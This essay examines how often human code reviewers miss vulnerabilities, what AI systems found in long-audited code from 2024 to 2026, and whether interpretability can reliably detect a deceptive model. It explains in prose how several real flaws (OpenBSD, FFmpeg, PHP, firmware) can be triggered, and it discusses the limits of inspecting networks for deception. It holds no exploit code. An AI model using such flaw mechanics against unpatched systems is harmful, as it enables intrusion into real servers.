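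No group reread the code without a warning, so part of the improvement could have come from reading it twice. But nobody found the ordinary bug on the second reading, which suggests that rereading did little to reveal problems people weren't looking for. Most of those who found the SQL injection on the second attempt said they had needed a reminder to think about security.

The warning helped about half of those who had missed the SQL injection but only about one in eight of those who had missed the negative number. Many developers have read about SQL injection and recognise its pattern. They also know what a negative number is, but to see the danger here they had to work out the attack themselves. Shellshock was hard to spot for a similar reason, since people knew how Bash imported functions but did not think of how an attacker could use this.

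People who often reviewed code did better in the first review, as did those who thought about vulnerabilities when writing their own code. Years of professional experience made no significant difference.

### Asking reviewers to think about security

*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) tested the reminder properly by giving it to some participants before they began. The 150 participants reviewed 160 lines of Java that registered website users. The code had two vulnerabilities. If the database returned an error, the program wrote the user's details, including password data, to a log file. It also protected stored passwords with MD5, an old scrambling method that attackers can break.

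The researchers randomly assigned each person to one of four groups:

| Instructions | People | Found the log flaw | Found the MD5 flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing about security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| The same, with a general 22-item checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with a 7-item checklist for this change | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

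Reviewers were much more likely to notice the log flaw if they had been asked to look for security problems. At these rates, a project drawing reviewers at random from the same pool would need about 75 without that instruction, or four with it, to have a 90 per cent chance that at least one would notice the flaw. The figure of 75 depends on one person's success, so the true number could easily be 20 or 30, but that is still many more than four.

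One person who missed the MD5 flaw had assumed there would be "some separate security assessment". NASA's developers had likewise read less carefully when they expected testing to follow.

The checklists made no measurable difference beyond the instruction, even though the general one had two items about these flaws and the short one included only items relevant to the change. With about 40 people in each group, the experiment could easily have missed a gain of ten percentage points. Of the 76 people who had a checklist, 32 said it helped, some because it made them go back to a line they had passed over.

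But a checklist can't help much if the reviewer lacks the relevant knowledge. One participant had considered MD5 during the review and judged it a good choice. After Heartbleed, Wheeler proposed a checklist item for confirming that the code validates every field from outside. This might work better because the reviewer looks for whether a check is present, which takes less specialist knowledge. That is a guess, and the result gives some reason to doubt it.

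### How often reviewers think about security

The low detection rates among reviewers given no instructions are probably the better guide to everyday reviewing, because few reviewers seem to think of security unprompted. Braz and Bacchelli surveyed 182 people who review code and first asked what kinds of problem they look for. Only nine mentioned security, but when a later question raised the subject, 111 said they always considered it. Most respondents worked on software where security mattered, for employers who expected them to protect it, but two thirds said their companies provided no security training.

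Di Biase and colleagues read a random sample of 1,155 comments that reviewers wrote in 2014 on changes to the Chromium browser. Eleven, about 1 per cent, raised a security problem.

Most changes contain no vulnerability, so even perfect reviewers would write few comments about vulnerabilities, and the small number here doesn't show neglect. If the sample was representative of the 60,655 comments it came from, reviewers raised roughly 300 to 1,000 security problems in those comments during the year. The researchers found 187 CVEs entered for Chromium in 2015. Many of the problems raised in review were probably too minor to have earned a CVE, so the two numbers don't give a detection rate, but they suggest that Chromium's reviewers stopped a good many vulnerabilities.

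### What real reviews caught and missed

Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021), in *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, studied Chromium OS, an operating system built around the browser, and compared code reviews in which reviewers caught a vulnerability with reviews in which they missed one. They searched the comments on 404,878 reviews for words such as "overflow" and "race", checked the results by hand, and found 516 in which a vulnerability had been caught. They also traced vulnerabilities reported later back to 374 reviews in which they had been missed.

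Reviewers did much better with some types than others:

| Type of flaw | Caught | Missed | Share caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calling a function known to be dangerous | 53 | 0 | 100% |
| Failing to release memory or another resource | 71 | 4 | 95% |
| Race conditions | 73 | 10 | 88% |
| Going outside a buffer | 42 | 16 | 72% |
| Poor control of who may do what | 8 | 58 | 12% |
| Failing to check input | 9 | 72 | 11% |
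| Using memory or another resource after releasing it | 3 | 62 | 5% |

Paul and colleagues attribute the pattern to how much code a reviewer has to understand. A reviewer can spot a call to a dangerous function on one line, but may have to follow memory through several files to see that a program uses it after releasing it.

This is plausible, but the last column does not give detection rates. Its figures depend on how many successful reviews the keyword search found and how many missed vulnerabilities people had discovered by the time of the study. The figure for race conditions is especially doubtful. In Qu's kernel data, race conditions stayed hidden for five years on average, so Chromium OS reviewers may have missed many that nobody had yet discovered. Fuzzers are good at finding unchecked input, so the cases of that type that reviewers missed would be discovered sooner.

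Di Biase and colleagues found that reviewers of the browser's code had caught 6 buffer errors and missed 18, almost the reverse of the proportion in Chromium OS. The two studies' results are closer for errors in which a program uses memory after releasing it. Di Biase and colleagues counted these errors together with other misuses of C++, the browser's main language, and found that reviewers had caught 8 and missed 33. This surprised them because they thought a reader could check for many of these errors by looking at the change and a little of the surrounding code.

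Paul and colleagues also compared reviews that caught a vulnerability with reviews that missed one. Reviewers were more likely to catch one when they had done a larger share of the file's earlier reviews, and when they had often worked with the change's author. They were less likely to catch one when the change was spread over many directories. The odds of catching a vulnerability were 4.55 times as high for bug fixes as for other changes, perhaps because reviewers read bug fixes more suspiciously.

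Reviewers who had done the most reviews overall were less likely to catch a vulnerability. The researchers suggest they may have been tired or rushed, but projects may also give their busiest reviewers the most difficult changes. Reviewers caught more in longer reviews, but finding a flaw may itself have lengthened the review, because the author then has to send a new version.

### Do more reviewers help?

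The number of reviewers had no significant effect in Chromium OS. Di Biase and colleagues thought that having more than two might help, because 39 of the 71 reviews in which somebody caught a vulnerability had more than two. But they did not report how many of the unsuccessful reviews did, so the two groups can't be compared. People also sometimes join a review because somebody is already suspicious, and, as with Meneely's Chromium data, riskier code may get more reviewers.

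Records like these can't show whether more reviewers catch more flaws as long as projects choose the number of reviewers according to the code. In the experiments, each flaw was found by some people and missed by others, so a second reviewer chosen at random would sometimes have caught what the first missed.

Thompson and Wagner studied more than 3,000 open-source projects and concluded in 2017 that code review reduces security bugs. According to the record of their data, *Code review regression analysis of open source GitHub projects*, they used two models to estimate how many of the issues in each project were security bugs. Projects that review more code probably also differ in other ways, such as having more developers or better tests, and statistical adjustment can account only for measured differences. The conclusion is plausible, but it doesn't establish what share of vulnerabilities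 a review catches.

### The order of the files

Review tools such as GitHub usually list the files in a change alphabetically. Fregnan, Braz and Çalikli (2022), in *First Come First Served*, examined 219,476 proposed changes to 138 Java projects and found that files nearer the top received more comments, even after allowing for differences such as the number of added lines. Shape of Code's *Impact of number of files on number of review comments* (2022) analysed the same data and estimated that comments fall by about 16 per cent with each file down the list. At that rate, the tenth file gets about a fifth as many comments as the first.

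Fewer comments do not necessarily mean fewer bugs caught, so *Does Order Matter?* (2026) examines whether a file's position is associated with later bug fixes. Fregnan and colleagues had already tested whether position affects bug detection by having people review two files, each with a planted mistake. Each file came first in half of the experimental conditions. The order made no difference for one mistake, but the odds of finding the other were 64 per cent lower when its file came last. For example, if 60 per cent of reviewers would find that mistake when its file came first, about 35 per cent would find it when the file came last.

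Reviewers with only two files to read can hardly have been exhausted by the second, so the effect of file order might be larger in a change with twenty files. If reviewers all start at the top of the same list and lose concentration towards the bottom, they will also tend to miss the same bugs, which makes their reviews less independent. A tool could easily reduce this overlap by showing each reviewer the files in a different order.

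### Reviewing with AI, and reviewing what AI wrote

By 2025 many developers were using AI to write code, to review it, or both. *S3C2 Summit 2025-03* (2025), a report on a meeting about software supply chain security, records that organisations wanted people to check all AI-generated code, which participants said took a great deal of work. If a heavy reviewing load partly explains why the busiest Chromium OS reviewers caught less, having more code to check would make the problem worse.

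Authors may also be less suspicious of code that an AI helped them write. *GitHub's Copilot Code Review* (2025) cites an experiment by Perry and colleagues in which developers using an AI assistant were more likely to submit insecure code than those without one, and were often more confident in it. The assistant is now very out of date, so the result is weak evidence about the quality of code from current models. The overconfidence may persist, since Basili and Selby's professionals also overestimated how many bugs they had found.

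AI can also help the reviewer. *Rethinking Code Review Workflows with LLM Assistance* (2025) describes a trial at the Swedish company WirelessCar, where developers used two AI assistants to review real code changes. One gave a complete review at the start, and the other answered developers' questions. Developers generally preferred to start with the AI's review, but this depended on how well they knew the code and how serious the change was.

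Preferences are weak evidence about detection rates, and most of Basili and Selby's professionals misjudged which technique had worked best. An AI review might draw people's attention to security, as the instruction did in 2022. It might also make them read less carefully, assuming the AI has already found the problems. Several reviewers who start from the same AI-written list may all miss whatever it leaves out. A version of the 2022 experiment could measure this by planting vulnerabilities and giving a randomly chosen half of the reviewers an AI assistant.

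### From volunteers to maintainers

A single reviewer's detection rate varied in the experiments. Among reviewers who had been told nothing about security, it ranged from 3 per cent for the log flaw to 65 per cent for SQL injection. Among those asked from the start to look for security problems, it was 46 per cent for the log flaw and 61 per cent for MD5.

These differences affect how far a clean report lowers the probability of a flaw. Suppose some code has a 50 per cent chance of containing a flaw like the MD5 one. A clean report lowers that chance only to 44 per cent if the reviewer had no particular instructions, but to 28 per cent if the reviewer was looking for security problems.

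Maintainers might do better than the volunteers because they know their code. In Chromium OS, reviewers who were familiar with the file tended to catch more vulnerabilities, but those who had simply done more reviews overall did not. Maintainers also live with the consequences of a mistake, and Braz and colleagues acknowledge that people may pay more attention when the stakes are higher.

There are also reasons to expect maintainers to do worse. The planted flaws were well-known types in short changes that contained everything a reader needed. A maintainer may have to review hundreds of lines across several directories, and the danger may depend on code outside the change. Knowing the program can also lead a maintainer to share the author's assumptions, as happened with Bash.

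The researchers' exclusions probably also raised the detection rates. In the 2021 experiment, 194 people went beyond the welcome page, but the results cover only 146. The researchers left out anyone who did not finish or who wrote no comments on the code. That was sensible for testing whether attentive people can see a vulnerability, but in an ordinary project a reviewer who approves a change without comment still counts as having reviewed it.

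## What AI systems found in code that had already been audited, 2024 to 2026

Since 2024, people have used language models to find serious flaws in code that experts had reviewed, audited and fuzzed for years. A language model is a program trained on a huge amount of text, including source code and descriptions of past bugs. Recent models can follow what a function does and often explain what is wrong with it.

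The first finds were modest. In October 2024, Google's Big Sleep project used a model to find a memory error in the database SQLite. The developers fixed it the same day, before it reached a release, so it is not evidence about long-lived bugs. A month later, Google announced that a fuzzer, running a harness written by a model, had found a memory error in OpenSSL that had probably been there for about twenty years.

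In May 2025 the security researcher Sean Heelan published a rough detection rate for OpenAI's model o3. Heelan had already found a vulnerability in the Linux kernel's code for sharing files with Windows machines, and gave o3 the relevant 3,300 lines a hundred times. The model reported the bug in 8 runs and produced 28 false alarms. When Heelan supplied about 12,000 lines, it reported the bug in only one of a hundred runs, but it also reported a similar bug that Heelan had not known about.

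A model can review the same code afresh as many times as somebody will pay for. If it detects a bug in 8 per cent of runs, which would be a poor rate for a human reviewer, a hundred independent runs are almost certain to find the bug at least once. At 1 per cent a run, the chance is about 63 per cent. Repetition doesn't help with a bug that the model has no chance of recognising.

### How a model searches a program

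In April 2026 the AI company Anthropic announced a model called Claude Mythos Preview, which it released only to selected organisations because of its skill at finding and exploiting vulnerabilities. Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview’s cybersecurity capabilities*, describe how they used it to search open-source projects:

1. The model ranks the project's files from 1 to 5 by how likely they are to contain an interesting bug. A file that only defines constants gets a 1, and one that interprets data from the internet might get a 5.
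2. Separate copies of the model start work on different files, beginning with the highest ranked. Each receives a short instruction that amounts to "find a security vulnerability in this program".
3. The copy reads the code and forms a hypothesis about what could go wrong. It then runs the program to test the hypothesis, adding debugging code if necessary, and tries another if the first one fails.
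4. It reports either that it found no bug, or a bug together with an input that triggers it.
5. Another copy reads the report and judges whether the bug is real and important.

The third step combines reading code with running it on test inputs, two methods that people have mostly used separately. Fagan's inspectors had only the text of the program, and a fuzzer mostly tries inputs without regard to what the code is for. A model that identifies a possible missing check can construct an input that would expose it, even if a fuzzer would take centuries to produce that input by chance.

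Running the program also rules out many false alarms. Carlini and colleagues mostly looked for memory errors, partly because AddressSanitizer, the checker Böck used in his Heartbleed trial, can confirm them. All 112 bug reports that an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.6, had produced for the Firefox browser proved to be real.

Because of this choice, the published finds also provide more evidence about missed memory errors than about other kinds of missed vulnerabilities. An address checker would not have detected Log4Shell, for example.

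### OpenBSD: a number both before and after

The oldest bug that Carlini and colleagues described dated from 1998. It was in OpenBSD, the security-focused operating system that Ozment and Schechter had studied, and it let anyone who could reach a machine over the network crash it.

When one computer sends data to another over TCP, the protocol behind most internet traffic, it numbers the bytes. The receiver acknowledges what has arrived so the sender can resend the rest. Originally, a receiver could acknowledge only an unbroken run of bytes from the beginning, so if one packet went missing, the sender had to resend everything after it. An extension proposed in October 1996 let receivers acknowledge separate ranges, and OpenBSD added it in 1998.

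OpenBSD keeps a list of "holes", the ranges of bytes that it has sent but the other side has not acknowledged. If it has sent bytes 1 to 20 and the other side has acknowledged 1 to 10 and 15 to 20, the list contains one hole, 11 to 14. When a new acknowledgement arrives, the kernel goes through the list and shrinks or deletes the holes that the acknowledgement fills. If the acknowledgement reveals a new gap further along, the kernel adds another hole to the end of the list.

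The code contained two mistakes. First, the kernel checked that the end of an acknowledged range was plausible but did not check the start. This is usually harmless, since acknowledging bytes −5 to 10 has the same effect as acknowledging 1 to 10.

Second, if a single acknowledgement deleted the only hole and added a new one, the kernel would try to attach the new hole to the deleted one and crash. That combination looked impossible because the acknowledged range had to start at or before the beginning of the hole to delete it, but after the highest byte acknowledged so far, which is further along, to add a new one.

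Both conditions can hold because the byte numbers are 32-bit, so the count returns to zero after about 4.3 billion, as a clock returns to one after twelve. OpenBSD in effect decided which of two numbers came first by going the shorter way round the clock. By this rule, 9 comes before 2, because going back from 2 to 9 takes five hours and going forward takes seven. But 9 also comes after 5, because it is four hours further on. If the hole starts at 2 and the highest acknowledged byte is 5, a range that starts at 9 passes both tests.

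Genuine byte numbers are never far enough apart for this to happen, but the code didn't check the start of the range, so an attacker could supply a number that was far enough away.

A careful reader could have noticed either mistake and still approved this code. The missing check did no harm in ordinary use. A reader could also have argued that the program would never reach the second mistake, and that argument, like Bentley's proof of binary search, would be sound for ordinary whole numbers. To find the vulnerability, a reader had to consider both mistakes together and remember how the computer compares the numbers.

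Finding the OpenBSD bug took about a thousand runs, which cost less than $20,000 in total and produced several dozen other findings. The run that found the bug cost under $50, but Carlini and colleagues point out that this figure only makes sense in hindsight, because nobody could have known which run would succeed. If "several dozen" means about forty, each finding cost about $500, not counting the work of checking it. For comparison, Trail of Bits' 2022 audit of curl took 9.5 weeks of expert work and recorded 14 issues. The comparison is rough because the programs differ, and the standards for counting a finding may differ too.

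One success in a thousand runs isn't a detection rate for this bug, because the runs were spread over many files and those examining other parts of the system had little chance of finding it.

### FFmpeg: a choice from 2003 and a rewrite from 2010

Nearly every large service that handles video depends on FFmpeg, a video-processing library. People have fuzzed it so heavily that there are research papers on how to fuzz such libraries. Mythos Preview found a flaw in FFmpeg's code for H.264, a very common video format.

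An H.264 frame consists of one or more slices, each made up of blocks of 16 by 16 pixels. When FFmpeg decodes a block, it sometimes uses data from a neighboring block, but only if both are in the same slice. It therefore keeps a table of the slice number for each block position. The largest number an entry can hold is 65,535, which FFmpeg uses to mean "no slice here yet". The counter that numbers the slices can go higher than 65,535.

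FFmpeg marks empty positions with the number 65,535, which can also be a slice number. Real video uses only a handful of slices in a frame, so the two uses never conflict. But if someone builds a frame with 65,536 slices, one of them has that number, and FFmpeg treats an empty position as a neighbouring block in the same slice and writes outside its buffer.

The choice of 65,535 dates from 2003, when the H.264 code was added. According to Carlini and colleagues, it became a vulnerability in 2010, when somebody restructured the code. A reviewer of the 2010 change would have had to know about a seven-year-old convention that may not have been visible in the code under review. A fuzzer could run every line involved millions of times without producing a frame with enough slices to trigger the bug.

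The flaw wasn't very dangerous. It let an attacker write only a few bytes in the wrong place, and the researchers thought it would be hard to exploit. They spent about $10,000 on several hundred runs over FFmpeg, which also found several other important vulnerabilities.

### OpenSSL and PHP

OpenSSL had far more money and attention after Heartbleed than before. In January 2026 the project released fixes for twelve vulnerabilities, all of which the start-up AISLE had found with its AI system. Three dated from between 1998 and 2000, so they were in the library when Ben Laurie spent a year auditing it for DARPA and when Neel Mehta was reading it in 2014. Nobody can say whether either of them read those lines. After Heartbleed, Raymond defended Linus's law by saying that there "weren't any eyeballs". That defence is harder to make for those flaws, which survived another eleven years in one of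 the most closely watched libraries in the world.

The most alarming finds of 2026 were two flaws in PHP, a programming language used on nearly 70 per cent of websites. The flaws would let an attacker take control of a web server without a password. Sabin (2026) reports in *AI uncovers massive flaw in web's foundational code* that both had existed for decades. PHP's maintainers released fixes on 21 October. Some site owners, including 4chan and the operators of certain Wikipedia services, took their sites offline until they could install the fixes.

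According to Krazit (2026), in *How the security community found the PHP flaws*, the security firm Calif found the flaws in August while taking part in a programme that gives open-source projects access to OpenAI's restricted security models. OpenAI's *Patch the Planet* gives a slightly different account, in which Calif used the model GPT-5.6 Sol to identify one critical flaw, and another firm, Wiz, independently discovered both. The maintainers and their partners then spent two months preparing the fixes.

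In both flaws, PHP uses memory at the wrong time. In one, as AndrewMohawk (2026) explains in *Picking apart PHP2Shell*, PHP marks part of an internal list as ready before it has finished filling it in. If something interrupts the work, PHP later treats the unfinished part as complete. In the other, a long-running PHP process keeps using a memory address after the request that owned the memory has ended.

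Even a security researcher who knows that a program contains a serious bug may start by looking in the wrong place. AndrewMohawk had started investigating before the fixes came out, when there were only rumours of two serious bugs. AndrewMohawk first suspected a different piece of code, in which PHP seemed to keep two addresses for too long, but tracing every reference showed that this code was sound.

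The first of the two flaws also resembled a known one. Calif's *A tale of two PHP remote vulnerabilities* begins with Stefan Esser's discovery in 2004 that PHP could be left in a dangerous state if it reached its memory limit at the wrong moment. Esser considered that vulnerability too serious to publish the attack. Anyone who worked on PHP's security could therefore have known for 22 years to check for interruptions of this kind.

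### Server firmware that nobody maintained

Firmware is the software that starts a computer before the operating system loads. Most hardware makers build theirs from EDK II, an open-source project. In October 2026, TianoCore, the organisation behind EDK II, published an advisory about a flaw in the code that starts a machine over a network, and rated the flaw's severity 9.5 out of 10.

The cause was an ordinary memory error. The code copies incoming error messages into a fixed-size buffer and miscalculates the lengths if a message is too big. Early reports called the flaw 16 years old because they dated it from code added in November 2010. The Hacker News' *Google and Anthropic AI Found an 18-Year-Old UEFI Flaw* (2026) explains that the same faulty calculation was in another part of the package by April 2008.

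The code had received most kinds of scrutiny that experts recommend. Faisal (2026), in *Anthropic's AI Found an 18-Year-Old Critical Flaw Hiding in Server Firmware*, relays Anthropic's account that maintainers had revised it four times, security auditors had reviewed it and fuzzing projects had targeted it. Researchers had also disclosed nine other vulnerabilities in the same package in January 2024, so people who understood attacks well had recently examined nearby code.

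The package had been without a designated maintainer since mid-2023, and in February 2026 TianoCore ranked it first among the unmaintained packages that needed one. This may help explain why nobody followed up the nine earlier discoveries with a thorough search, but it can't explain the first fifteen years.

Google's firmware security team found the flaw in May 2026. Its system, built on Google's Gemini models, compares possible findings, removes duplicates and tests whether an attacker could reach the code before an engineer sees a report. Anthropic found the same flaw in early September with an unreleased model that had only the source code to work from. The model also wrote a fix and tests for it. Anthropic's researchers checked both before sending the fix to the maintainers.

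The maintainers accepted a fix on 15 October, but each manufacturer has to build and test its own version, and server owners then have to restart their machines. Anthropic's *Finding and fixing an 18-year-old vulnerability in server firmware* (2026) warns that the fix could take months to reach machines in use.

### When two searches find the same bug

Two laboratories found the EDK II flaw about four months apart, after it had gone unreported for eighteen years. Two firms also found the PHP flaws separately. Rescorla asked whether attackers would have found a published flaw anyway. If two defenders found the same old flaw within months of each other, an attacker with similar tools could probably have found it too. According to Faisal, Anthropic drew the same conclusion about EDK II.

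One shared bug is not enough for a capture–recapture estimate, in which a large overlap between two searches would mean that few bugs remain. People also notice shared discoveries and write about them, while a flaw that only one laboratory found gets an ordinary advisory.

A large overlap could mean that both laboratories were finding nearly everything. But their models learned from much of the same public code and many of the same bug reports, so they might instead be finding and missing the same kinds of bug. Knight and Leveson's programmers shared blind spots of this kind. If the models do too, a clean report from one laboratory would add little to a clean report from the other.

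### Better models or more money?

Some of the success may reflect how much people were spending. Epoch AI's *Are Mythos’ cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026), a review of the public evidence up to June, distinguishes the skill of discovering a vulnerability from that of exploiting it, which means working out how to make the program do what an attacker wants.

The evidence clearly showed that AI systems had become better at exploiting bugs. Epoch AI, a research group that tracks progress in AI, combined results from about fifteen tests and estimated that Mythos Preview was seven months ahead of the previous trend, with a plausible range of three to thirteen months. In one of Anthropic's own trials, Opus 4.6 turned known Firefox bugs into working attacks twice in several hundred attempts, while Mythos Preview produced 181 working attacks.

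The evidence about discovery was more ambiguous. At 21 large organisations, the number of serious vulnerabilities entered in the CVE catalogue was 142 per cent above the 2025 level in April and 262 per cent above in May. But Anthropic had just offered organisations up to $100 million of free use of its models to secure their software. Older models might have found many of the same flaws if somebody had paid for as many runs.

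Epoch AI gives some support for this. AISLE reported that even small, freely available models could recognise several of the vulnerabilities that Anthropic had showcased. However, recognising a flaw in code that somebody has already picked out is easier than finding one. Mozilla, which makes Firefox, considered Mythos Preview as good as elite security researchers but noted that it had found no entirely new kinds of vulnerability.

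Anyone choosing a model needs to know whether better models or bigger budgets led to these finds, but the answer makes little difference to what the finds show about human reading. People had failed to report the OpenBSD bug for 27 years, regardless of what it cost to find.

### Had somebody already noticed?

A more relevant objection is that people had already found some of these bugs, or very similar ones. Mythos Preview also discovered a vulnerability in the file server of the FreeBSD operating system and wrote an attack that gave complete control of the machine. Critics pointed out that a fix for the same kind of mistake in related code was already public.

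Carlini and colleagues had argued that a model can't have found a previously unknown bug by remembering the answer from its training. The FreeBSD case weakens this argument because, although the bug was new, the model could have learned the pattern from a related bug that was already public. This makes the discovery less impressive as a feat of reasoning.

As evidence about human readers, though, it is at least as damaging, because FreeBSD's developers and auditors could also have read the earlier fix and searched their own code for the same mistake. Dirty COW also survived because nobody did this kind of search. Comparing a lot of code with a known pattern is dull work for people, but the tedium doesn't hinder a model.

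Ferreira (2026), in *PHP vulnerability post-mortem reveals bug was known two years ago*, reports that a small team of PHP maintainers had known of the vulnerability since 2024. Tom's Hardware's *OpenAI says ChatGPT Sol helped uncover critical PHP flaws* describes a bug that had stumped human developers for two years before researchers, with AI help, turned it into working attacks in two weeks.

People had noticed the cause of the PHP bug before an AI system found it, though only after about twenty years. As with GHOST in 2013, they had not established how dangerous it was. Wiz said that exploiting the flaws required "an exceptionally complex chain of steps", and the repair involved major changes to the PHP engine, which maintainers would understandably be reluctant to make for a bug that might be harmless. The AI's main contribution may have been to settle whether the repair was worth making.

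### False alarms and overloaded maintainers

Companies that sell AI systems have an interest in publicising their successes. In *What should we take from Anthropic’s (possibly) terrifying new report on Mythos?* (April 2026), Marcus quoted a sceptic who did not doubt some of the results but thought it unclear under what conditions the model had found the bugs and how people had been involved.

The criticism was fair, because more than 99 per cent of the vulnerabilities Anthropic had found were still unpatched, so it could not publish their details. It did publish cryptographic fingerprints of many of the unpublished reports. A fingerprint reveals nothing about a report's contents, but once the report is published, anyone can check that it existed in April and has not changed since. Anthropic also disclosed the number of runs and the cost for OpenBSD and FFmpeg, which a company would leave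 out if it wanted people to think that every run succeeds.

The fingerprints cover only bugs the model found, so they can't show how many it missed. This selection matters less when judging human readers than it did with the famous bugs, because one confirmed flaw from 1998 proves that people missed it, whatever the model failed to find elsewhere.

Many reports from AI systems are also wrong. Google runs a programme that pays people to report vulnerabilities in its open-source projects, such as the Go programming language. On 1 October 2026, the programme stopped accepting reports of flaws in the software itself. Google said this was because automated submissions had risen sharply and the "vast majority" were not valid (Markovic, 2026, *AI slop submissions force Google to freeze its open-source bug bounty*).

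By contrast, all 112 reports for Firefox were correct. The difference is probably due to checking. Anthropic's researchers ran the program, confirmed the memory error with AddressSanitizer and, for the most serious bugs, paid specialists to review the report before it went to a maintainer. In 89 per cent of 198 reviewed reports, the specialists gave the bug exactly the same severity as the model had. Someone hoping for a quick reward can ask a weaker model for a list of vulnerabilities and submit all of them without checking them.

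Sending a false report takes almost no effort, but a maintainer has to read the code to reject it. If one report in twenty is real and each takes an hour to assess, the project spends twenty hours of skilled work on each real vulnerability before anyone starts to fix it. If maintainers start to skim the reports, they may also dismiss a real one.

Accurate reports also create work for maintainers. Anthropic said it checked bugs by hand partly to avoid flooding maintainers, but might eventually have to relax this practice because there were so many bugs. In October, Axios reported that AI bug reports were overwhelming the maintainers of OpenSSL. For some projects, the slow part of repairing old bugs has shifted from finding them to deciding which reports to believe and writing fixes that don't introduce new bugs.

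### How much human reading had missed

The confirmed old bugs show that earlier human searches were incomplete, and their number is the least those searches could have missed. Like the famous cases, they don't show what share of bugs those searches caught.

Curl is one of the few projects with records good enough for a rough estimate of the share of vulnerabilities that earlier searching had found. By July 2025, 167 were known, and the June 2026 release added 18 to that total. If nearly all of the 18 were already in the code in July 2025, the first 27 years or so of searching had found at most 167 out of 185, or about 90 per cent. The share is lower if any others remain undiscovered, and it could be much lower.

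The same project shows that one AI search doesn't find everything. Mythos Preview examined curl before the June release and produced five reports. One was a low-severity vulnerability and four were false alarms. Stenberg saw no evidence that it found more than the AI tools curl had already been using. Epoch AI inferred that the earlier tools had apparently found everything Mythos Preview could have found. That may be true of that search, but the 18 fixes in the June release suggest that much remained for other searches to find.

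In a larger comparison, Anthropic tested several models on about a thousand projects in OSS-Fuzz. It ran each model once on each of roughly 7,000 entry points, the places where a program takes in data, and graded the worst crash the model could cause. Opus 4.6 and another model of the same generation each caused about 250 to 275 crashes, nearly all in the two mildest grades. Mythos Preview caused 595 in those two grades. It also took full control of ten programs, all with the latest fixes installed.

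The older models had therefore caused fewer than half as many crashes in the same code. If we count every crash that Mythos Preview caused as a detectable bug, an older model's detection rate in a single run was at most about 46 per cent. If some code had a 50 per cent chance of containing such a bug, a clean report from the older model would have lowered that chance only to about 35 per cent. More runs would have helped find some of the missed bugs, but perhaps not those beyond the older model's ability.

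These figures measure a model's ability to cause a crash as well as its ability to notice a mistake, and a model may identify a possible bug without being able to trigger it. The figures also rest on the assumption that the newer model found every bug. Fagan likewise treated the bugs found in the first six months of use as the full set. The next model to read this code will probably find bugs that Mythos Preview missed.

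## What the record implies for human inspection of neural networks

The AI systems that found these old bugs are also programs that people would like to check. Engineers can review the code that trains and runs a language model, but that code explains little of what the model does. Most of the model's behaviour comes from its weights, billions of numbers that an automatic training process adjusts until the model does well at its task. The model is a neural network, which turns an input into numbers and combines them with the weights layer by layer to produce an output. The intermediate results, called activations, change with every input.

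Interpretability researchers try to work out what a network is doing from its weights and activations. A feature is something meaningful, such as a car in a picture, that the network represents, usually as a pattern across many activations. A circuit is a set of features and the weights that connect them, such as those that recognise a car from its wheels and windows. Methods that look inside the network like this are called white-box methods, while black-box methods use only its inputs and outputs.

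### Reading a program that nobody wrote

Olah (2022), in *Mechanistic Interpretability, Variables, and the Importance of Interpretable Bases*, compared this work with reverse engineering, in which someone works out what a compiled program does without its source code. The parts correspond roughly as follows:

| Ordinary program | Neural network |
|---|---|
| Compiled program | Weights |
| Processor that runs it | Architecture, the fixed arrangement of layers |
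| Contents of memory | Activations |
| Variable | Feature |

Olah expected understanding a network to be at least as hard as reverse-engineering a large, complicated program. People often manage that eventually, even with a whole operating system, because a program, like a network's weights, is a finite description of what happens on an enormous number of possible inputs.

A reverse engineer has to work out which parts of memory hold which variables. The equivalent for a neural network is finding its features, which Olah thought was arguably the central task of interpretability. This is hard because many neurons, the single units in a layer, respond to several unrelated things. The usual explanation is superposition, in which a network represents more features than it has neurons by spreading them over overlapping groups of neurons. This works because most features are seldom needed at the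 same time, but it means nobody can list the features by going through the neurons one by one.

Enumerative safety is the hope of showing that a network is safe by listing everything it represents and finding nothing dangerous on the list. A complete list would cover dangers that nobody had thought to test for, which no set of tests can do. Researchers would still have to read it carefully, because a model trained on novels and crime reports will probably have a feature for deception whether or not it ever deceives anyone. They would have to show that the feature plays no part in how the model treats its users.

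### The argument from software

The history of long-lived bugs suggests an argument against relying on this kind of inspection:

1. Programmers write source code for other people to read, in languages with exact rules.
2. Experts have nevertheless missed serious flaws in it for years.
3. Nobody wrote a network's weights to be read, and current descriptions of networks are partial.
4. So if experts inspect a network and find nothing dangerous, this is weak evidence that nothing dangerous is there.

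Source code has these advantages, though not always to the same degree. OpenSSL had confusing variable names, and the Bash manual never explained how Bash passed functions on. But a reader of either program could look up what each line of C was supposed to do. A network's arithmetic is just as exact, and anyone with the weights can calculate its output. No manual gives the meaning of a feature, though, so researchers have to infer it from examples. Olah therefore compares networks with compiled programs, whereas almost all the evidence about reviewers comes from source code.

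It is less clear how often experts miss such flaws, but in experiments a single reviewer's chance of noticing a planted vulnerability ranged from 3 to 65 per cent.

Even if all three premises are true, the conclusion doesn't strictly follow. Someone who overlooks a missing bounds check might still notice a network's plan to deceive people, much as a poor proofreader can tell that a letter is threatening. The software record is a good reason to doubt a clean report on a network until somebody has measured how often such inspections detect problems, but it can't supply that rate.

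### How much of a network the tools describe

Some direct evidence supports the premise that descriptions of networks are partial. One common tool is the sparse autoencoder, a second network that rewrites the original model's activations as a combination of a few entries from a long list of candidate features. People or another model then label each entry by looking at the text that triggers it. Researchers can test how much the list leaves out by putting the rewritten activations back into the original model and measuring how much worse the model performs.

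By this test, the tools of 2024 left out a lot. In *Lucius Bushnaq's Shortform*, Bushnaq (2024) estimated that inserting one of the best sparse autoencoders at a single layer usually made a model predict text only as well as one trained with less than a tenth, or even a hundredth, of the computing power. Tracing a circuit would mean inserting several at once, which could make the predictions even worse. Bushnaq added that the usual way of reporting these results made the damage look small, and that an autoencoder that captured only 10 per cent of the features might hardly change the score.

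Neel Nanda, who leads an interpretability team at Google DeepMind, replied that the conversion into computing power was difficult and that "we just don't know how to evaluate SAE [sparse autoencoder] quality". A year later, a commenter on Nanda's essay *Interpretability will not reliably find deceptive AI* estimated that the best explanations accounted for no more than 20 to 50 per cent of the tiny parts of a model they were meant to explain. These are informal estimates, and the tools have changed since. Researchers still have no agreed figure for how much of a modern model's behaviour anyone can explain, which is itself a problem for a method that depends on a complete list.

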